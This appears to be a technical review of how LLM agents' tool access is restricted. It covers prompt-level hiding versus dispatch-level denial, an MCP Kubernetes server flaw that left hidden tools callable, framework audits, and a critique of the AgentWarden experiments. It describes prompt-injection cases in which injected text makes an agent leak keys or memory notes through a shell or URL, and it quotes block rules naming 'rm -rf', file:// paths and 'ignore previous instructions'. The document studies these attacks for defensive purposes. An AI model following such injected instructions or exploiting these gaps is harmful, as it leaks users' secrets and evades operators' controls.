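Per-call authorization gets a "No" on A and D even though it can stop attacks that the two simpler designs can't. These scores mean that its safety depends on somebody writing a correct rule for every dangerous value, as the safety of Hardy's compiler did. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao come closer to D by making each call declare a purpose and rejecting tokens issued for a different one. But the model writes the declaration, so an attacker who controls the model's output can also choose the purpose, and they don't treat the declaration as proof that the call is benign. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) doesn't call its own per-call system an object-capability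 system, because the model still names resources with strings.

Dispatch-level denial also does not prevent indirect access. A session without a shell tool may be able to message another session that has one. If the second session runs commands on request, the first has authority over the shell without permission to use it, and this authority does not appear in the first session's list of allowed tools.

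An allowlist of whole tools looks a lot like the POSIX capability flags, which Miller and colleagues score "no" on A, D and G. One `web_fetch` entry covers every address on the web, just as the file-ownership flag covers every file on the machine. Both schemes also fix the set of permissions in advance. Noyan, for example, labels each of 600 workplace tasks with the permissions it needs from a list of 15. A list like this can separate tasks that need email from tasks that don't, but it can't limit a task to one recipient.

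The comparison is a little unfair to tools, because the operating system fixes the flags while a developer can make a tool as narrow as they like. LangChain, which makes software for building agents, documents a tool called `get_user_info` that takes the user's identity from the application's configuration instead of from the model, so in a given session it can only look up one user. If the harness creates a separate version of a tool for each session and fills in the sensitive arguments itself, a tool name in a session table is very close to a true reference.

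### Two injected requests

Suppose a harness has 15 tools and a user asks it to summarise an online article. For this session, the harness shows the model only the four tools that Sidik and Rokach list for the task: `read`, `web_fetch`, `memory_search` and `memory_get`. It hides the other 11, including the shell tool, `exec`. An attacker wrote the article, and we assume the model obeys any instruction in it.

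In one version, the article tells the model to call `exec` with a command that sends the user's private login key to the attacker's server. In the other, it tells the model to read a private note from memory and then call `web_fetch` with an address on the attacker's server that ends with the note's text. The request delivers the note, whatever the server sends back.

| Design | Request for `exec` | Request for `web_fetch` |
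| --- | --- | --- |
| Prompt-level hiding | No check applies. The dispatcher finds `exec` and runs the command. | No check applies. The tool sends the note. |
| Dispatch-level denial | The check on the tool's name refuses the call, whatever the command is. | The check on the name allows the call, and the tool sends the note. |
| Per-call authorization | The check on the tool's name refuses the call. | The check on the address decides. |
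| True references | The lookup fails, because the session has no reference to a shell. | The lookup fails if the session has references only to particular pages. With a general fetching function, the note gets out. |

Checking the address is the hard part. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) describes ScopeGate, which checks each tool call. The "gates" in the title are lists of tools. ScopeGate looks for the tool's name in a policy, compares each restricted argument with a list of allowed values, and refuses the call if either test fails or causes an error. Mellafe Zuvic also requires that the policy never come from the model's output, because an injection that corrupts the call could corrupt the policy too.

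If the user asks for a summary of one article, the policy can allow only that article's address. But the user might also ask for a summary of everything the article links to, and the attacker's page would then supply the other addresses. If the harness allows only the exact links on the page, the model can't add the private note to one of them. If it allows any address on the linked websites, and the attacker owns one of those websites, the model could send the attacker the note as part of an address.

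Even the exact list leaks a little information, because the model chooses which link to fetch and the attacker's server can see the choice. With 256 links on the page, each fetch could reveal one byte of the note. References to the individual links would leak at the same rate. Both designs still work as intended, since every fetch goes to an allowed page. To stop the leak, the system would have to track how the private note influenced the choice, as the higher-overhead version of Rajani and colleagues' labels does.

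### What one broad tool brings back

Removing tools achieves much less if the session keeps a shell, so the number of tools is a poor measure of what an agent can do. Suppose a coding session loses 14 of its 15 tools and keeps only `exec`. That is a 93 percent reduction, compared with 73 percent for the summarising session, but the agent can still read files with `cat`, fetch web pages with `curl`, and write files or send messages with a short script. Bouras and colleagues note that an unrestricted command can reach the network, read secrets, rewrite a project's history and install software, all with the user's privileges.

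Limiting the shell to certain commands helps, but it's hard to do well. Bouras and colleagues split each command line into its parts and check every part, so permission to run the testing program `pytest` doesn't cover a second command added after a semicolon. But `pytest` runs code from the project, including any code an attacker put there. Their check also allows search commands such as `grep`, which can read files outside the folders the agent's file-reading tool may open. They conclude that the process still needs a sandbox, which places operating-system restrictions on what it can do.

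A shell can't restore every ability an agent loses when its other tools are hidden. If a separate server holds the key to the mail system and refuses requests from the shell's account, no shell command can send mail through that system. The damage a broad tool can do depends on the references and credentials it can reach.

Tools that look narrow can also be broad. Sidik and Rokach saw a model try to open a local file by giving `web_fetch` an address beginning with `file://`. Their check on the arguments caught the attempt, but a list of allowed tool names wouldn't have, because `web_fetch` was on the list.

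### The best case for hiding

Hiding a tool is still useful, even though it isn't a security boundary. The main benefit is fewer attempts, as Uppala's experiment showed. Many injected instructions describe a goal without naming a tool, such as "send this file to the following address". A model can easily comply if it sees an email tool, but may give up if it sees nothing suitable. The attacker then has to know or guess the tool's name, which is trivial for a popular open-source program but may be hard for a company's private tools.

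Hiding tools also reduces honest mistakes and shortens the prompt, which are the reasons LangChain gives for narrowing a large set of tools. But a harness that hides a needed tool by mistake may cause the kind of improper call it was meant to prevent. Yin and colleagues also tested models that could see one irrelevant tool, such as a calculator for a question about the weather, but not the one they needed. Qwen3-32B misused the irrelevant tool or invented a more suitable one in 46.6 percent of cases, compared with 5.1 percent when it had no tools.

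A hidden list is also harder to steal. Tool names can reveal which payment service a company uses or what its staff can do to a customer's account, and a model can't disclose names that never enter its context. To keep the list secret, the dispatcher should return the same error for a hidden tool as for one that doesn't exist. If it returns "not permitted" for one and "unknown tool" for the other, an attacker who can see the replies can find the hidden tools by guessing names.

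## What deployed software does when a model names an unlisted tool

Some deployed software refuses calls to the tools it hides, and some runs them. The two kinds are easy to confuse because the model receives the same short list of tools either way.

### A Kubernetes server that filtered only its list

Kubernetes runs software across a cluster of machines. The open-source MCP server `mcp-server-kubernetes` lets an agent manage a cluster with tools such as `kubectl_get` for looking up resources, `kubectl_delete` for deleting them and `exec_in_pod` for running commands inside the cluster. Its documentation described three settings as access controls. `ALLOW_ONLY_READONLY_TOOLS` and `ALLOW_ONLY_NON_DESTRUCTIVE_TOOLS` each selected a group of safer tools, and `ALLOWED_TOOLS` took a list of tool names.

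All three settings shortened the server's reply to `tools/list`, the MCP request for the list of available tools, but none affected `tools/call`, the request that runs a tool. GitHub's *GHSA-CR22-WJX7-2W6M* (2026), the security advisory on this flaw (CVE-2026-46519), traces it to two functions in the same source file. The function that handled list requests applied the filter, but the one that handled call requests looked up the tool by name and ran it with no equivalent check. The advisory describes the access control as "effectively cosmetic".

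Francisco Rosales of Manifold Security discovered the problem. In tests on a live cluster under each of the three settings, `kubectl_delete` didn't appear in the list, but a direct call to it still worked. An attacker needed only a connection to the server and a tool's name, which anyone could look up in the project's public source code.

The server also had an access token, but it controlled only who could connect. A client meant to use only `kubectl_get` could connect with a valid token and then delete resources. According to GitHub, this mattered because the project supports several clients sharing one server over a network, and operators relied on the settings to limit what different users could do.

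An injected instruction might not have been enough to exploit the flaw, because a harness that looks up names only among the tools the server listed rejects `kubectl_delete` before contacting the server. But the operator of a shared server can't count on every client to do this.

GitHub rated the flaw 8.8 out of 10, or "high". The rating reflects an attack that is easy to carry out over the network, needs few privileges and no action by a user, and could expose, change or destroy data. The US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD) had not added its own rating when its page on the flaw, *CVE-2026-46519 Detail* (2026), appeared in June.

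The damage depended on the permissions of the server's Kubernetes account. Where that account had full administrator rights, which the advisory says is common in development and staging systems, anyone who could reach the server could take over the cluster. If an operator had given the account read-only permissions, Kubernetes would have refused the deletion that the MCP server passed on, providing the protection that the three settings only appeared to provide.

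According to MITRE's official record, *mcp-server-kubernetes Affected By Tool Access Control Bypass* (2026), the CVE number was reserved on 14 May 2026 and the record was published on 11 June. GitHub's advisory appeared on 21 May. Version 3.6.0 fixes the flaw by changing the settings from prompt-level hiding to dispatch-level denial. It applies the list's filter at the start of the call function too, so a call to any tool outside the allowed set now returns an error.

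These records contain no evidence of a real attack, but they can't rule one out. In MITRE's record, a note dated 11 June from CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, lists exploitation as "poc", meaning that a public demonstration existed. The note doesn't show what happened on private clusters before or since. OSV's *CVE-2026-46519* (2026) lists every version before 3.6.0 as affected but gives the change that introduced the flaw as unknown, so it is unclear how long servers were exposed. An attack might also be hard to find in old logs, because the server handled forbidden and permitted calls the same way.

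The fix covers only tool names. *CSIC Cyber Advisory Critical Argument Injection Vulnerability Contained Within MCP Server Kubernetes*, from California's emergency services office (Cal OES), describes another flaw in this server, CVE-2026-61459, rated 9.8. That flaw involved a call's arguments and could let an attacker steal credentials and take over the whole cluster.

### What the protocol requires

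The current MCP specification requires servers to "implement proper access controls" and validate all tool inputs, as did the November 2024 version (Model Context Protocol, 2024). But the specification doesn't define "proper" or explicitly require a server to refuse calls to a tool it left out of the caller's list.

The nearest thing to such a rule is Model Context Protocol's requirement that a server's list contain the tools "currently available to the requesting client". The most natural reading is that the server should refuse a call to an unlisted tool, since it would be strange to leave a tool out as unavailable and then run it. The specification also recommends, but does not require, that a human always be able to deny a call.

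A request doesn't show whether the client ever saw the tool. tianpan.co's *The MCP Tool List Grew Mid-Session and Your Agent Called a Tool* (2026) points out that a call has no field for this, and that the server couldn't verify the information if it did. A model that guesses a common name such as `create_issue` can therefore run a tool the server has just added.

Honest clients will sometimes have an outdated tool list. The July 2026 revision lets a server specify how long clients may keep a copy, and the example in the specification allows five minutes. A client could therefore call a tool that the server has since withdrawn, or not yet know about one that the server would run. So the server has to decide what the caller may run when the call arrives, regardless of which tools the client has seen.

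The revision also ended one common way of hiding tools. Under the old rules, a database server could start by listing only `connect_database` and add `query` and `list_tables` once the model had called it. Alexander (2026) explains in *Sessionless MCP via Explicit State Handles* that servers may no longer change the list as a side effect of a call. The server should instead list `query` and `list_tables` from the start and require a `connection_id`, which the model gets from `connect_database`. A query without a valid identifier fails, so the server controls access by checking an argument instead of hiding the tool.

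Alexander's reasons had more to do with consistency and caching than with security, but they show why an MCP session was a poor unit for restricting an agent. ChatGPT created a new session for every tool call, while most desktop programs kept one session from launch until the user closed the program. A restriction tied to a session would have lasted for one call in ChatGPT and covered every conversation in most desktop programs.

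Operators who don't trust a server's own checks can now also check calls at a *gateway*, a program that sits between agents and servers. Model Context Protocol (2026), the announcement of the July revision, explains that the tool's name now travels in an HTTP header called `Mcp-Name` as well as in the message body, so a gateway can refuse a call without opening the body. A server can also have clients copy selected arguments into headers, such as the region in which a database query should run.

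A gateway like this could have protected a Kubernetes server with the flaw described above, provided that clients could not bypass it and that the name in the header matched the one in the body. Many developers seem to rely on other people's code for such details, since the main MCP software kits get half a billion downloads a month, according to Model Context Protocol's announcement.

### An audit of three frameworks

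Many developers use a framework, a software library that supplies a dispatcher, instead of writing their own. In June 2026, Mellafe Zuvic published an audit of three frameworks: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe.

The audit was a reading of the public source code to find out whether, after the model writes a call, the framework checks the actual argument values against a fixed policy before the tool runs, and refuses the call if the check fails. The audit lists the exact commits, or saved versions of the code, so anyone can repeat it.

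| Framework | Commits | How it finds the tool | Limits by default |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| LangChain | `00ad96c` | Looks up the name in `name_to_tool_map` | The tools in the map, and usually the form of the arguments |
| LangGraph | `bdb323e` | Looks up the name in `tools_by_name` | The tools in the map, and usually the form of the arguments |
| LlamaIndex | `520aa4e` (version 0.14.23) | Builds `tools_by_name` and checks that the name is in it | The tools in the map |
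| Stripe Agent Toolkit | `0b4961f` (classic) and `f54c9e6` (main) | Exposes the actions on a fixed allowlist | The allowlist, and the permissions of the Stripe key |

All three limit which tools exist, and none of them checks argument values against a policy by default. When a model names a tool that isn't in LlamaIndex's map, for example, the framework returns a not-found message to the model. This is dispatch-level denial if the developer builds a separate map for each session, but only prompt-level hiding if the map holds every tool and the developer shortens only the list in the prompt.

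The missing check matters most for Stripe's toolkit, because it can move money. The allowlist and the key's permissions can determine whether an agent may issue refunds at all, but not whether a particular refund should go to a particular customer. Within those limits, the toolkit passes along the amount, currency, customer and redirect address that the model wrote.

Mellafe Zuvic also tested a call, written in advance, that would change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. The test used real LangChain tools connected to a simulated merchant account. LangChain's normal dispatcher ran the call, and the payout account changed. A similar test on LlamaIndex found the same gap. Since no model had to write the call, these tests show only what the dispatchers do with it, not how often a model can be tricked into writing one.

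Developers can add protection to these frameworks. LangChain has an optional component that asks a person to approve calls, and a tool's author can build a similar step into a LlamaIndex tool. But a developer who doesn't know about the gap won't get either protection. According to Mellafe Zuvic, developers can't rely on a check in a LangChain callback (a function that runs when a certain event happens), because the callback's return value doesn't reliably block the call. ScopeGate is meant to fill the gap.

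The audit doesn't describe any of this as a vulnerability, and that seems right. The Kubernetes server's documentation described a restriction that its code didn't enforce. The frameworks leave developers to check values, which is a risky default, but they don't claim to do the checking themselves.

Reading source code can establish that a gap exists in a given version, but not how many developers have left it open, because any checks they added are in their own code. The audit also doesn't cover the MCP server that Stripe runs remotely, which may have further checks. And we can't infer how common the problem is elsewhere from three frameworks chosen by one researcher.

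A survey of open-source MCP servers could estimate how many filter the tools they list but not the calls they accept. Alexander used this approach to find out how many projects would break if sessions ended, taking a random sample of 1,000 servers and having a language model classify each one. In 90 percent of them, the application code didn't refer to sessions at all, and 2.5 percent stored application data by session.

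Exploitation is harder to measure because doing so requires records from running systems, and those records may be poor. For instance, LlamaIndex treats a call to a missing tool as an ordinary result for the model to read rather than as a security event, so an operator may never learn that an agent tried to use a tool it shouldn't have known about.

### Checking the name before the harness gets it

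A tool call passes through the model provider's interface before it reaches the harness, so the provider can reject an unlisted name first. Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) found in *Takedown* that the OpenAI, Gemini and Grok interfaces checked the tool names in returned calls against the developer's list, but Anthropic's didn't.

This has changed at least in part, because developers can now turn on Anthropic's strict mode. It's less clear whether the interface rejects unlisted names when strict mode is off, or when it's unavailable, as with the browser and desktop tools. It's safest to assume that the harness needs its own check.

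Lee and colleagues note that no standard specifies who must do this check. A harness developer may assume that the provider does it while the provider leaves it to the harness, in which case nobody does it. One of the eight coding agents they examined would run its file-writing tool even in read-only mode because it didn't validate the calls it received.

*Constrained decoding* prevents a model from naming an unlisted tool in a call. A model writes text in small pieces called tokens, and at each step it gives every token in its vocabulary a probability. The software around the model normally picks from the likely tokens, but with constrained decoding it first sets the probability of any token that couldn't continue a valid call to zero. If a session offers only `read` and `web_fetch`, the model can only write one of those two names where the tool's name goes, even if an injected instruction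 has made `exec` by far the most likely choice. The model can still write `exec` in its ordinary prose, which is harmless unless the harness searches the prose for calls.

"Strict" means different things in different software, and often it refers only to a call's arguments. OpenAI states that its strict mode makes the arguments follow the tool's schema, on supported models and for supported kinds of schema. mistral.rs is an open-source program for running models. Its documentation, *Strict tool calling*, states that its strict mode constrains only the arguments, and only if the model calls a tool that has the setting turned on.

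A different setting, usually called "allowed tools", restricts which tools the model may name. XGrammar, a library for constrained decoding, describes it as limiting the model to a predefined set of tools. In an example from mistral.rs' *Allowed tools*, a request describes both `get_weather` and `book_flight` but allows only `get_weather`. This is the reverse of prompt-level hiding, since the model is given the flight tool's description but isn't supposed to be able to call the tool.

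Under either setting, a value that fits the schema can still be unsafe. OpenAI's *Function calling* gives an example of a horoscope tool whose schema requires a text field called `sign` and forbids any others. Both "Aquarius" and "banana" fit this schema.

A schema can also list the permitted values, as the weather tool's does for "celsius" and "fahrenheit". A harness could write a new schema for each session that permits only the user's own payout account, and constrained decoding would then stop the model from writing any other. A model constrained this way couldn't have produced the bad call in Mellafe Zuvic's test. But the test gave the call straight to LangChain's dispatcher, which would still have run it, so the harness would have to check the value again there.

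### Tools that are meant to run while hidden

Systems with deferred loading, where the model finds tools through a search, differ in what they do if the model names a tool before it is loaded. OpenAI's JavaScript interpreter doesn't let a program use the tool. With Anthropic's `defer_loading`, the developer decides whether to refuse the call.

lean-ctx, an open-source MCP server, goes further and makes hidden tools callable on purpose. When it shortens its list, it always includes a tool called `ctx_call`, which can run any registered tool by name. A comment in the source code explains that this keeps the hidden tools "reachable". The Kubernetes server had much the same behaviour by accident. It isn't a flaw in lean-ctx, where the short list exists for convenience, but an operator who mistook the list for a restriction would be just as exposed.

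A tool like `ctx_call` also weakens checks that other software makes. A gateway that reads only the `Mcp-Name` header will find `ctx_call` there, because the name of the tool that `ctx_call` runs is in the arguments. An operator who allows `ctx_call` in effect allows every tool it can call, much as an operator who allows a shell allows the commands it can run.

Deferred loading can be safe if the harness keeps two lists. The dispatcher enforces the first, which contains the tools the session may run. The second is a shorter list of the tools currently shown to the model. The search should cover only the first list, so that the model can find more tools without gaining any that the session may not run.

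Enforcement takes little code in Myko, another MCP server. A developer can install a filter on tool names, which the server uses to decide both which tools to list and which to run. A second filter can then inspect the arguments, for example to allow only certain values of `playbook_id`. Both filters are ordinary functions outside the model. Neither is installed by default, and without a name filter Myko allows every tool.

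GitHub's system for running agents on software projects does more than filter which tools an agent can see. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, the industry body that hosts MCP, a gateway does that filtering, the MCP server behind it is read-only, and changes go through a separate job with its own permissions. If the server's credentials are also read-only, an agent that gets past the gateway and names a hidden tool for making changes still can't change anything through that server.

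## An experiment with a capability governor

AgentWarden, which Sidik and Rokach published in April 2026, is a capability governor combined with a proxy that checks each call. It hides tools, denies their use and inspects what the model writes. Any of these could make an attack fail, so only some of its experiments could test the claim that an agent can't misuse a tool it doesn't know exists.

### From the user's message to a shorter list

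Sidik and Rokach installed AgentWarden on OpenClaw, mostly with DeepSeek-chat as the agent's model. When a session starts, a small language model based on Qwen2.5-1.5B reads the user's first message and assigns the session to one of six task types. If its confidence is below 0.7, which happens in about 12 percent of sessions, it assigns the type "unknown". Each type has a minimum set of tools, which Sidik and Rokach worked out by hand from 500 OpenClaw sessions.

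| Task type | Minimum tools |
| --- | --- |
| Summarisation | `read`, `memory_get`, `web_search` |
| File read | `read`, `memory_get` |
| Web research | `web_search`, `web_fetch`, `read` |
| Code execution | `read`, `write`, `edit` |
| Email | `read`, `sessions_send` |
| Unknown | `read`, `web_search`, `memory_get` |

Despite its name, the code execution type has no tool for running code. The governor's actual lists can differ from these minimums, as with the four tools it gave the summarising session.

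Choosing the type this early helps security because a malicious web page that the agent opens later can't change which tools the session has. But a session that begins as a summary and turns into a coding job would keep the summariser's tools.

The governor then edits two files. It names the permitted tools in a notice in `AGENTS.md`, a text file that OpenClaw includes in the system prompt. It also lists the denied tools under `tools.deny` in `openclaw.json`, OpenClaw's configuration file.

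The deny list hides the tools, not the notice. OpenClaw sends tool definitions to the model separately from the notice, so a model could be told it has four tools and still see the definition of `exec`. According to OpenClaw's documentation, tool policy applies before the model is called, and the model doesn't receive the definition of a tool that the policy removes. OpenClaw also calls this policy "the hard stop" on what an agent can run. The documentation is newer than the version Sidik and Rokach tested, but if that version worked the same way, one setting produced both prompt-level hiding and dispatch-level denial.

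A deny list is easy to get wrong. OpenClaw's *Configuration — tool policy* warns that denying `write` doesn't deny `apply_patch`, which also changes files. Any unlisted tool stays available, including one that a later update adds, whereas an allow list would block it. `tools.deny` is also a global setting, so if AgentWarden rewrites it for every session, two sessions running at once would share whichever list it wrote last. OpenClaw's separate lists for each agent would avoid this.

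OpenClaw now offers a stricter setting, `tools.gatewayPolicy`, which accepts only an explicit list of permitted tools and, for some tools, permitted actions. It checks each call at run time, after any add-on code has had a chance to rewrite it. The check also covers tools that call other tools, so a general-purpose tool like lean-ctx's `ctx_call` wouldn't restore access to tools the policy leaves out.

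### The proxy

AgentWarden's other main component is a proxy between OpenClaw and the program that runs the model. It passes each request to the model, looks for tool calls in the reply, and evaluates them before OpenClaw receives them.

Fixed rules run first and take about 0.1 milliseconds. They block every call to `exec`, and to `sessions_spawn` and `subagents`, which start or control other agents. They also block calls whose arguments contain certain patterns, such as the deletion command `rm -rf`, an address beginning with `file://`, or the path to a login key. Other rules detect typical injection phrases like "ignore previous instructions".

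If a call passes the rules, the same small model that selected the task type allows or blocks it, which takes about 800 milliseconds. Calls to tools that Sidik and Rokach consider safe, including `read` and `web_search`, skip this step. When the proxy blocks a call, it removes the call from the reply, notifies the agent, and logs the event.

These checks are a form of per-call authorization, but their rules cover what is dangerous in general, not what the user asked for, so they can detect a request for a login key but not a payment to the wrong person.

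### What the learned policy is rewarded for

AgentWarden can take its tool lists from hand-written rules, but Sidik and Rokach consider learning the lists their main contribution. They measure a list with the *Skill Economy Ratio* (SER):

SER = number of tools the agent used ÷ number of tools it was given

An agent that summarises a document with one of its 15 tools has a ratio of 1/15, or 0.067. A ratio of 1 means that the agent used all its tools.

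The learned policy is a small neural network. Its input is the task type and a trust level, and its output is a yes or no for each of 17 tools, which makes 131,072 possible lists. Sidik and Rokach trained it by reinforcement learning, in which the network tries different lists and shifts towards those that earn more reward. The reward is

R = αU − βC − γP, with α = 1, β = 0.3 and γ = 5.

U is 1 if the task succeeds and 0 if it fails. C is 1 − SER, so it penalises unused tools. P is the number of calls the proxy blocked.

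Suppose the agent completes a summary with one tool and the proxy blocks nothing. With 15 tools on the list, the reward is 1 − 0.3 × 14/15 = 0.72. With four tools, it is 0.775, and if the list contains only the tool the agent used, it is 1. Each blocked call subtracts 5 points, far more than any success can add.

However, this penalty covers only the dangers that the proxy detects. In the earlier attack, a summarising agent reads a private note from memory and sends it out through `web_fetch`. A normal session that uses only `web_fetch` has a ratio of 1/4. The hijacked session also uses `memory_get`, which raises its ratio to 2/4. If the proxy allows both calls and the agent still finishes the summary, the reward rises from 0.775 to 0.85.

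The ratio also ignores how powerful each tool is. A session whose only tool is a shell gets a perfect 1 as soon as it runs a command. Sidik and Rokach prevent this with fixed limits that the policy can't override. The policy may never offer `sessions_spawn` or `subagents`, and it may offer `exec` only at trust level 4 or above on a scale from 0 to 5. Even at those levels, the proxy's rules refuse every `exec` call, so a highly trusted user's agent could see a shell tool that never works.

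### The 500-task batch

For summarising, the governor cut the list from 15 tools to four and removed every tool that Sidik and Rokach class as dangerous. This result describes the configuration and doesn't measure what happens in an attack.

Their largest experiment on OpenClaw had 400 ordinary tasks and 100 adversarial ones. The adversarial tasks included prompt injections, attempts to talk the model into acting without restrictions, and attempts to steal credentials. The proxy intercepted 447 tool calls and blocked 117 of them, including all 70 calls to `exec` and all 8 to `sessions_spawn`.

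Of the 100 adversarial tasks, the proxy blocked 38 and DeepSeek-chat refused 54. The other 8 led to no dangerous tool call. Sidik and Rokach therefore report that no attack succeeded, and add 38 and 54 to get "92%" coverage.

A rule that refuses every `exec` call is certain to block all 70. It is more surprising that the model wrote 70 such calls, because the governor is supposed to remove `exec` from ordinary sessions.

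The governor was probably off, and the agent had all 17 tools. Sidik and Rokach give the batch's average SER as 0.053, which their appendix describes as the "uncontrolled" value for an agent with all 17. The call count is consistent with this, since the agent made 447 calls in 500 tasks, or 0.894 per task, and 0.894 ÷ 17 is 0.053. With four tools, the ratio would have been about 0.22. The batch therefore tested the proxy and DeepSeek-chat's willingness to refuse, and it provides no evidence about hiding tools.

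Many of the blocked shell calls probably came from ordinary tasks. The proxy blocked 38 adversarial tasks. If all 78 calls to `exec` and `sessions_spawn` had come from those tasks, they would have averaged more than two such calls each, while the batch as a whole averaged less than one call of any kind per task. Blocking a shell command in an ordinary coding task may be sensible, but it doesn't stop an attack. The small model also wrongly blocked about 22 harmless file writes, such as scripts for a web server.

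The attacks that Sidik and Rokach describe in detail were mostly blunt, such as a prompt telling the model to pretend it had no restrictions and run a shell command. These are direct requests rather than indirect prompt injections, so how often a model refuses them is weak evidence of how often it would refuse injected instructions.

The proxy mattered more for weaker models. Qwen2.5 7B wrote `exec` calls under attack where DeepSeek-chat refused, and the proxy blocked them. A small version of Google's Gemma 4 that runs on a 6 GB graphics card wrote calls to `exec` or `sessions_spawn` in response to four of eight adversarial prompts, and the proxy blocked them all. These samples are small, but a large one isn't necessary to test a fixed rule on a tool's name, because the rule works the same way however the attacker persuaded the model.

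### What the ablation separates

An *ablation* switches off parts of a system to find out what each part contributes. Sidik and Rokach ran the same 100 tasks under four conditions.

| Condition | Average SER | Tools given | Tools called | Block rate |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Complete system | 0.227 | 4.5 | 1.01 | 4.8% |
| Hand-written rules instead of the learned policy | 0.177 | 5.8 | 1.00 | 13.7% |
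| No proxy | 0.225 | 4.5 | 1.00 | 12.1% |
| No AgentWarden | 0.078 | 13.0 | 1.01 | 5.6% |

The agent called about one tool per task in every condition, so the SER is roughly 1 divided by the number of tools given, which is 0.077 for 13 tools and 0.22 for 4.5. The improvement in the ratio therefore reflects only the shorter tool list.

Judging by the table, the governor with hand-written rules produced about two-thirds of the gain in SER, raising the ratio from 0.078 to 0.177. The learned policy added the remaining third, bringing it to 0.227. Sidik and Rokach credit the governor with about 80 percent of the gain. They may have divided 0.177 by 0.227, which gives 78 percent, but that is a share of the final ratio, not of the gain.

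The proxy contributed almost nothing to the ratio, yet Sidik and Rokach call it "the sole mechanism preventing dangerous tool calls from reaching execution". This is hard to reconcile with their design, because the deny list is also supposed to stop denied tools from running. If the proxy was the only protection, the deny list wasn't working and the governor was only changing what the model was told. Whether or not the deny list worked, Sidik and Rokach don't credit hiding with stopping any dangerous calls.

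The ablation doesn't show which reading is right, because its results don't include the number of dangerous calls that ran. The block rates don't settle it either. They are above zero in both conditions that had no proxy, so they may count calls that the proxy *would* have blocked. If so, the agent with 13 tools made fewer such calls than the agent with 4.5, even though a shorter list should reduce them.

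None of the four conditions isolates prompt-level hiding, because every condition with the governor on includes both the notice and the deny list. To test hiding alone, an experimenter could remove `exec` from the definitions sent to the model, leave it in OpenClaw's own table, and turn off the proxy's blocking. Some attacks would name `exec` and supply its arguments, while others would only describe a goal. The experimenter would count the calls the model wrote separately from the calls that ran.

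Uppala's results suggest that hiding `exec` would greatly reduce calls to it in the goal-only attacks. In the attacks that name `exec`, the outcome would depend on how often the model copied the name into a call, and every such call would run. A third condition, in which the model sees `exec` but the dispatcher refuses calls to it, would show how much protection comes from denial alone.

*Progressive Skill Discovery as Access Control for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Stettler, Girardet and colleagues, 2026) describes a later governor in which one server both delivers the tools and enforces their limits. Combining the tool list and the check makes a mismatch between them less likely.

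### A small effect on AgentDojo

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) is a benchmark that tests indirect prompt injection. An agent works with simulated email, Slack messages, travel bookings and bank accounts. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. The attack success rate is the share of attacked cases in which the agent carries out the attacker's malicious actions.

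Sidik and Rokach ran DeepSeek-chat with and without AgentWarden on 97 user tasks and 949 attacked cases. They used a standard attack called "important instructions", which tells the agent to do the attacker's task before the user's. *SecOPD* (2026) gives the number of cases in each of the four groups.

| Group | Attacked cases | Attack success without AgentWarden | Attack success with AgentWarden |
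| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Workspace | 560 | 96.1% | 95.7% |
| Travel | 140 | 83.6% | 80.0% |
| Banking | 144 | 92.4% | 92.4% |
| Slack | 105 | 65.7% | 60.0% |
| All | 949 | 90.3% | 88.9% |

Overall, successful attacks fell from 857 to 844, a difference that chance could easily explain. If we treat the two runs as independent, the 95 percent confidence interval for the change runs from about 4 percentage points fewer successes to about 1 point more. Benign utility fell from 90.7 to 89.7 percent, a difference of one task out of 97.

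Sidik and Rokach say they expected a small effect because the attack puts text into tool *outputs*, whereas AgentWarden governs tool *calls*. They describe the two as "complementary threat surfaces".

This explains how the attack reaches the model but not how it does harm. Debenedetti and colleagues explain that each attacker's goal in AgentDojo comes with a sequence of tool calls that would achieve it. One goal is to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account, and another is to email the attacker a security code. AgentWarden handled 2,070 tool calls during the defended run. If the reported success rate is right, the proxy had the chance to stop hundreds of malicious calls but let nearly all of them through.

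A better explanation is that AgentWarden had no rule against them. Its fixed rules cover shells, other agents, and arguments such as the path to a login key, but not bank transfers. A rule banning all transfers would also stop the user from paying bills. Only the account number distinguishes the attacker's payment from the user's, and AgentWarden had no record of which account the user meant to pay.

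The governor probably did little in this test either. None of its task types covers banking or travel, and its learned policy can switch only the 17 OpenClaw tools on and off. The result is therefore weak evidence for or against tool scoping. AgentDojo's own tool filter, which picks tools for each task, is a more direct test.

The 90.3 percent baseline is also a problem because it is far higher than other researchers have found for DeepSeek models. *The Same Zero* (2026) reports 4.3 percent for DeepSeek-chat on the banking tasks with four other attacks, compared with 92.4 percent in Sidik and Rokach's table. The newer DeepSeek-v4-Pro stayed below 10 percent in *AutoDojo* (2026). Different versions and attacks could explain some of the gap, but it is very large.

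The order of the groups in Sidik and Rokach's table is also unusual, with Workspace highest and Slack lowest. Slack is normally the easiest to attack and Workspace much harder. In *Kairos* (2026), for example, attacks on an undefended GPT-4.1 succeeded in 88.6 percent of Slack cases and 35 percent of Workspace cases. *CommandSans* (2025) found the same order for three undefended models.

A reversed score would explain both oddities. Some software reports the share of attacks that the agent *avoided*, as the "Security" score does in Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*, a version of the benchmark for another testing framework. If Sidik and Rokach's figures also show attacks avoided, the true attack success rate was 9.7 percent without AgentWarden and 11.1 percent with it. Slack would then be the highest group, at 34.3 percent without AgentWarden, and Workspace the lowest, at 3.9 percent. This is only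 a guess, and checking it would require the logs of the runs. If it is right, AgentWarden did slightly worse than no defence, but the difference is still 13 cases and could still be due to chance.

### Limits of the policy, the classifier and the proxy

Sidik and Rokach acknowledge that during training the learned policy collapsed to offering a single tool, which gave it a perfect SER of 1. They blame the simulated environment, which assumed that an agent uses a fixed fraction of whatever tools it has. Real agents sometimes need a tool that nobody predicted.

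In 20 live sessions, the policy's ratio was 0.557. Sidik and Rokach compare this with the 0.053 from the 500-task batch and give the improvement as 337 percent in some places and 952 percent in another. The larger figure fits the two ratios, which differ by a factor of about 10.5, but the ratios come from different tasks. In the ablation, which used the same tasks throughout, the improvement was 191 percent.

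Sidik and Rokach trained the small model that judges calls on only 273 examples. Of these, 95 percent were calls to block, so only about 14 were calls to allow. They say this imbalance led it to block harmless file writes. The model made no errors on a test of 11 calls, but a model that gets one call in five wrong would do the same about one time in twelve. They call the test a "smoke test" and estimate that a production system would need 2,000 to 5,000 balanced examples.

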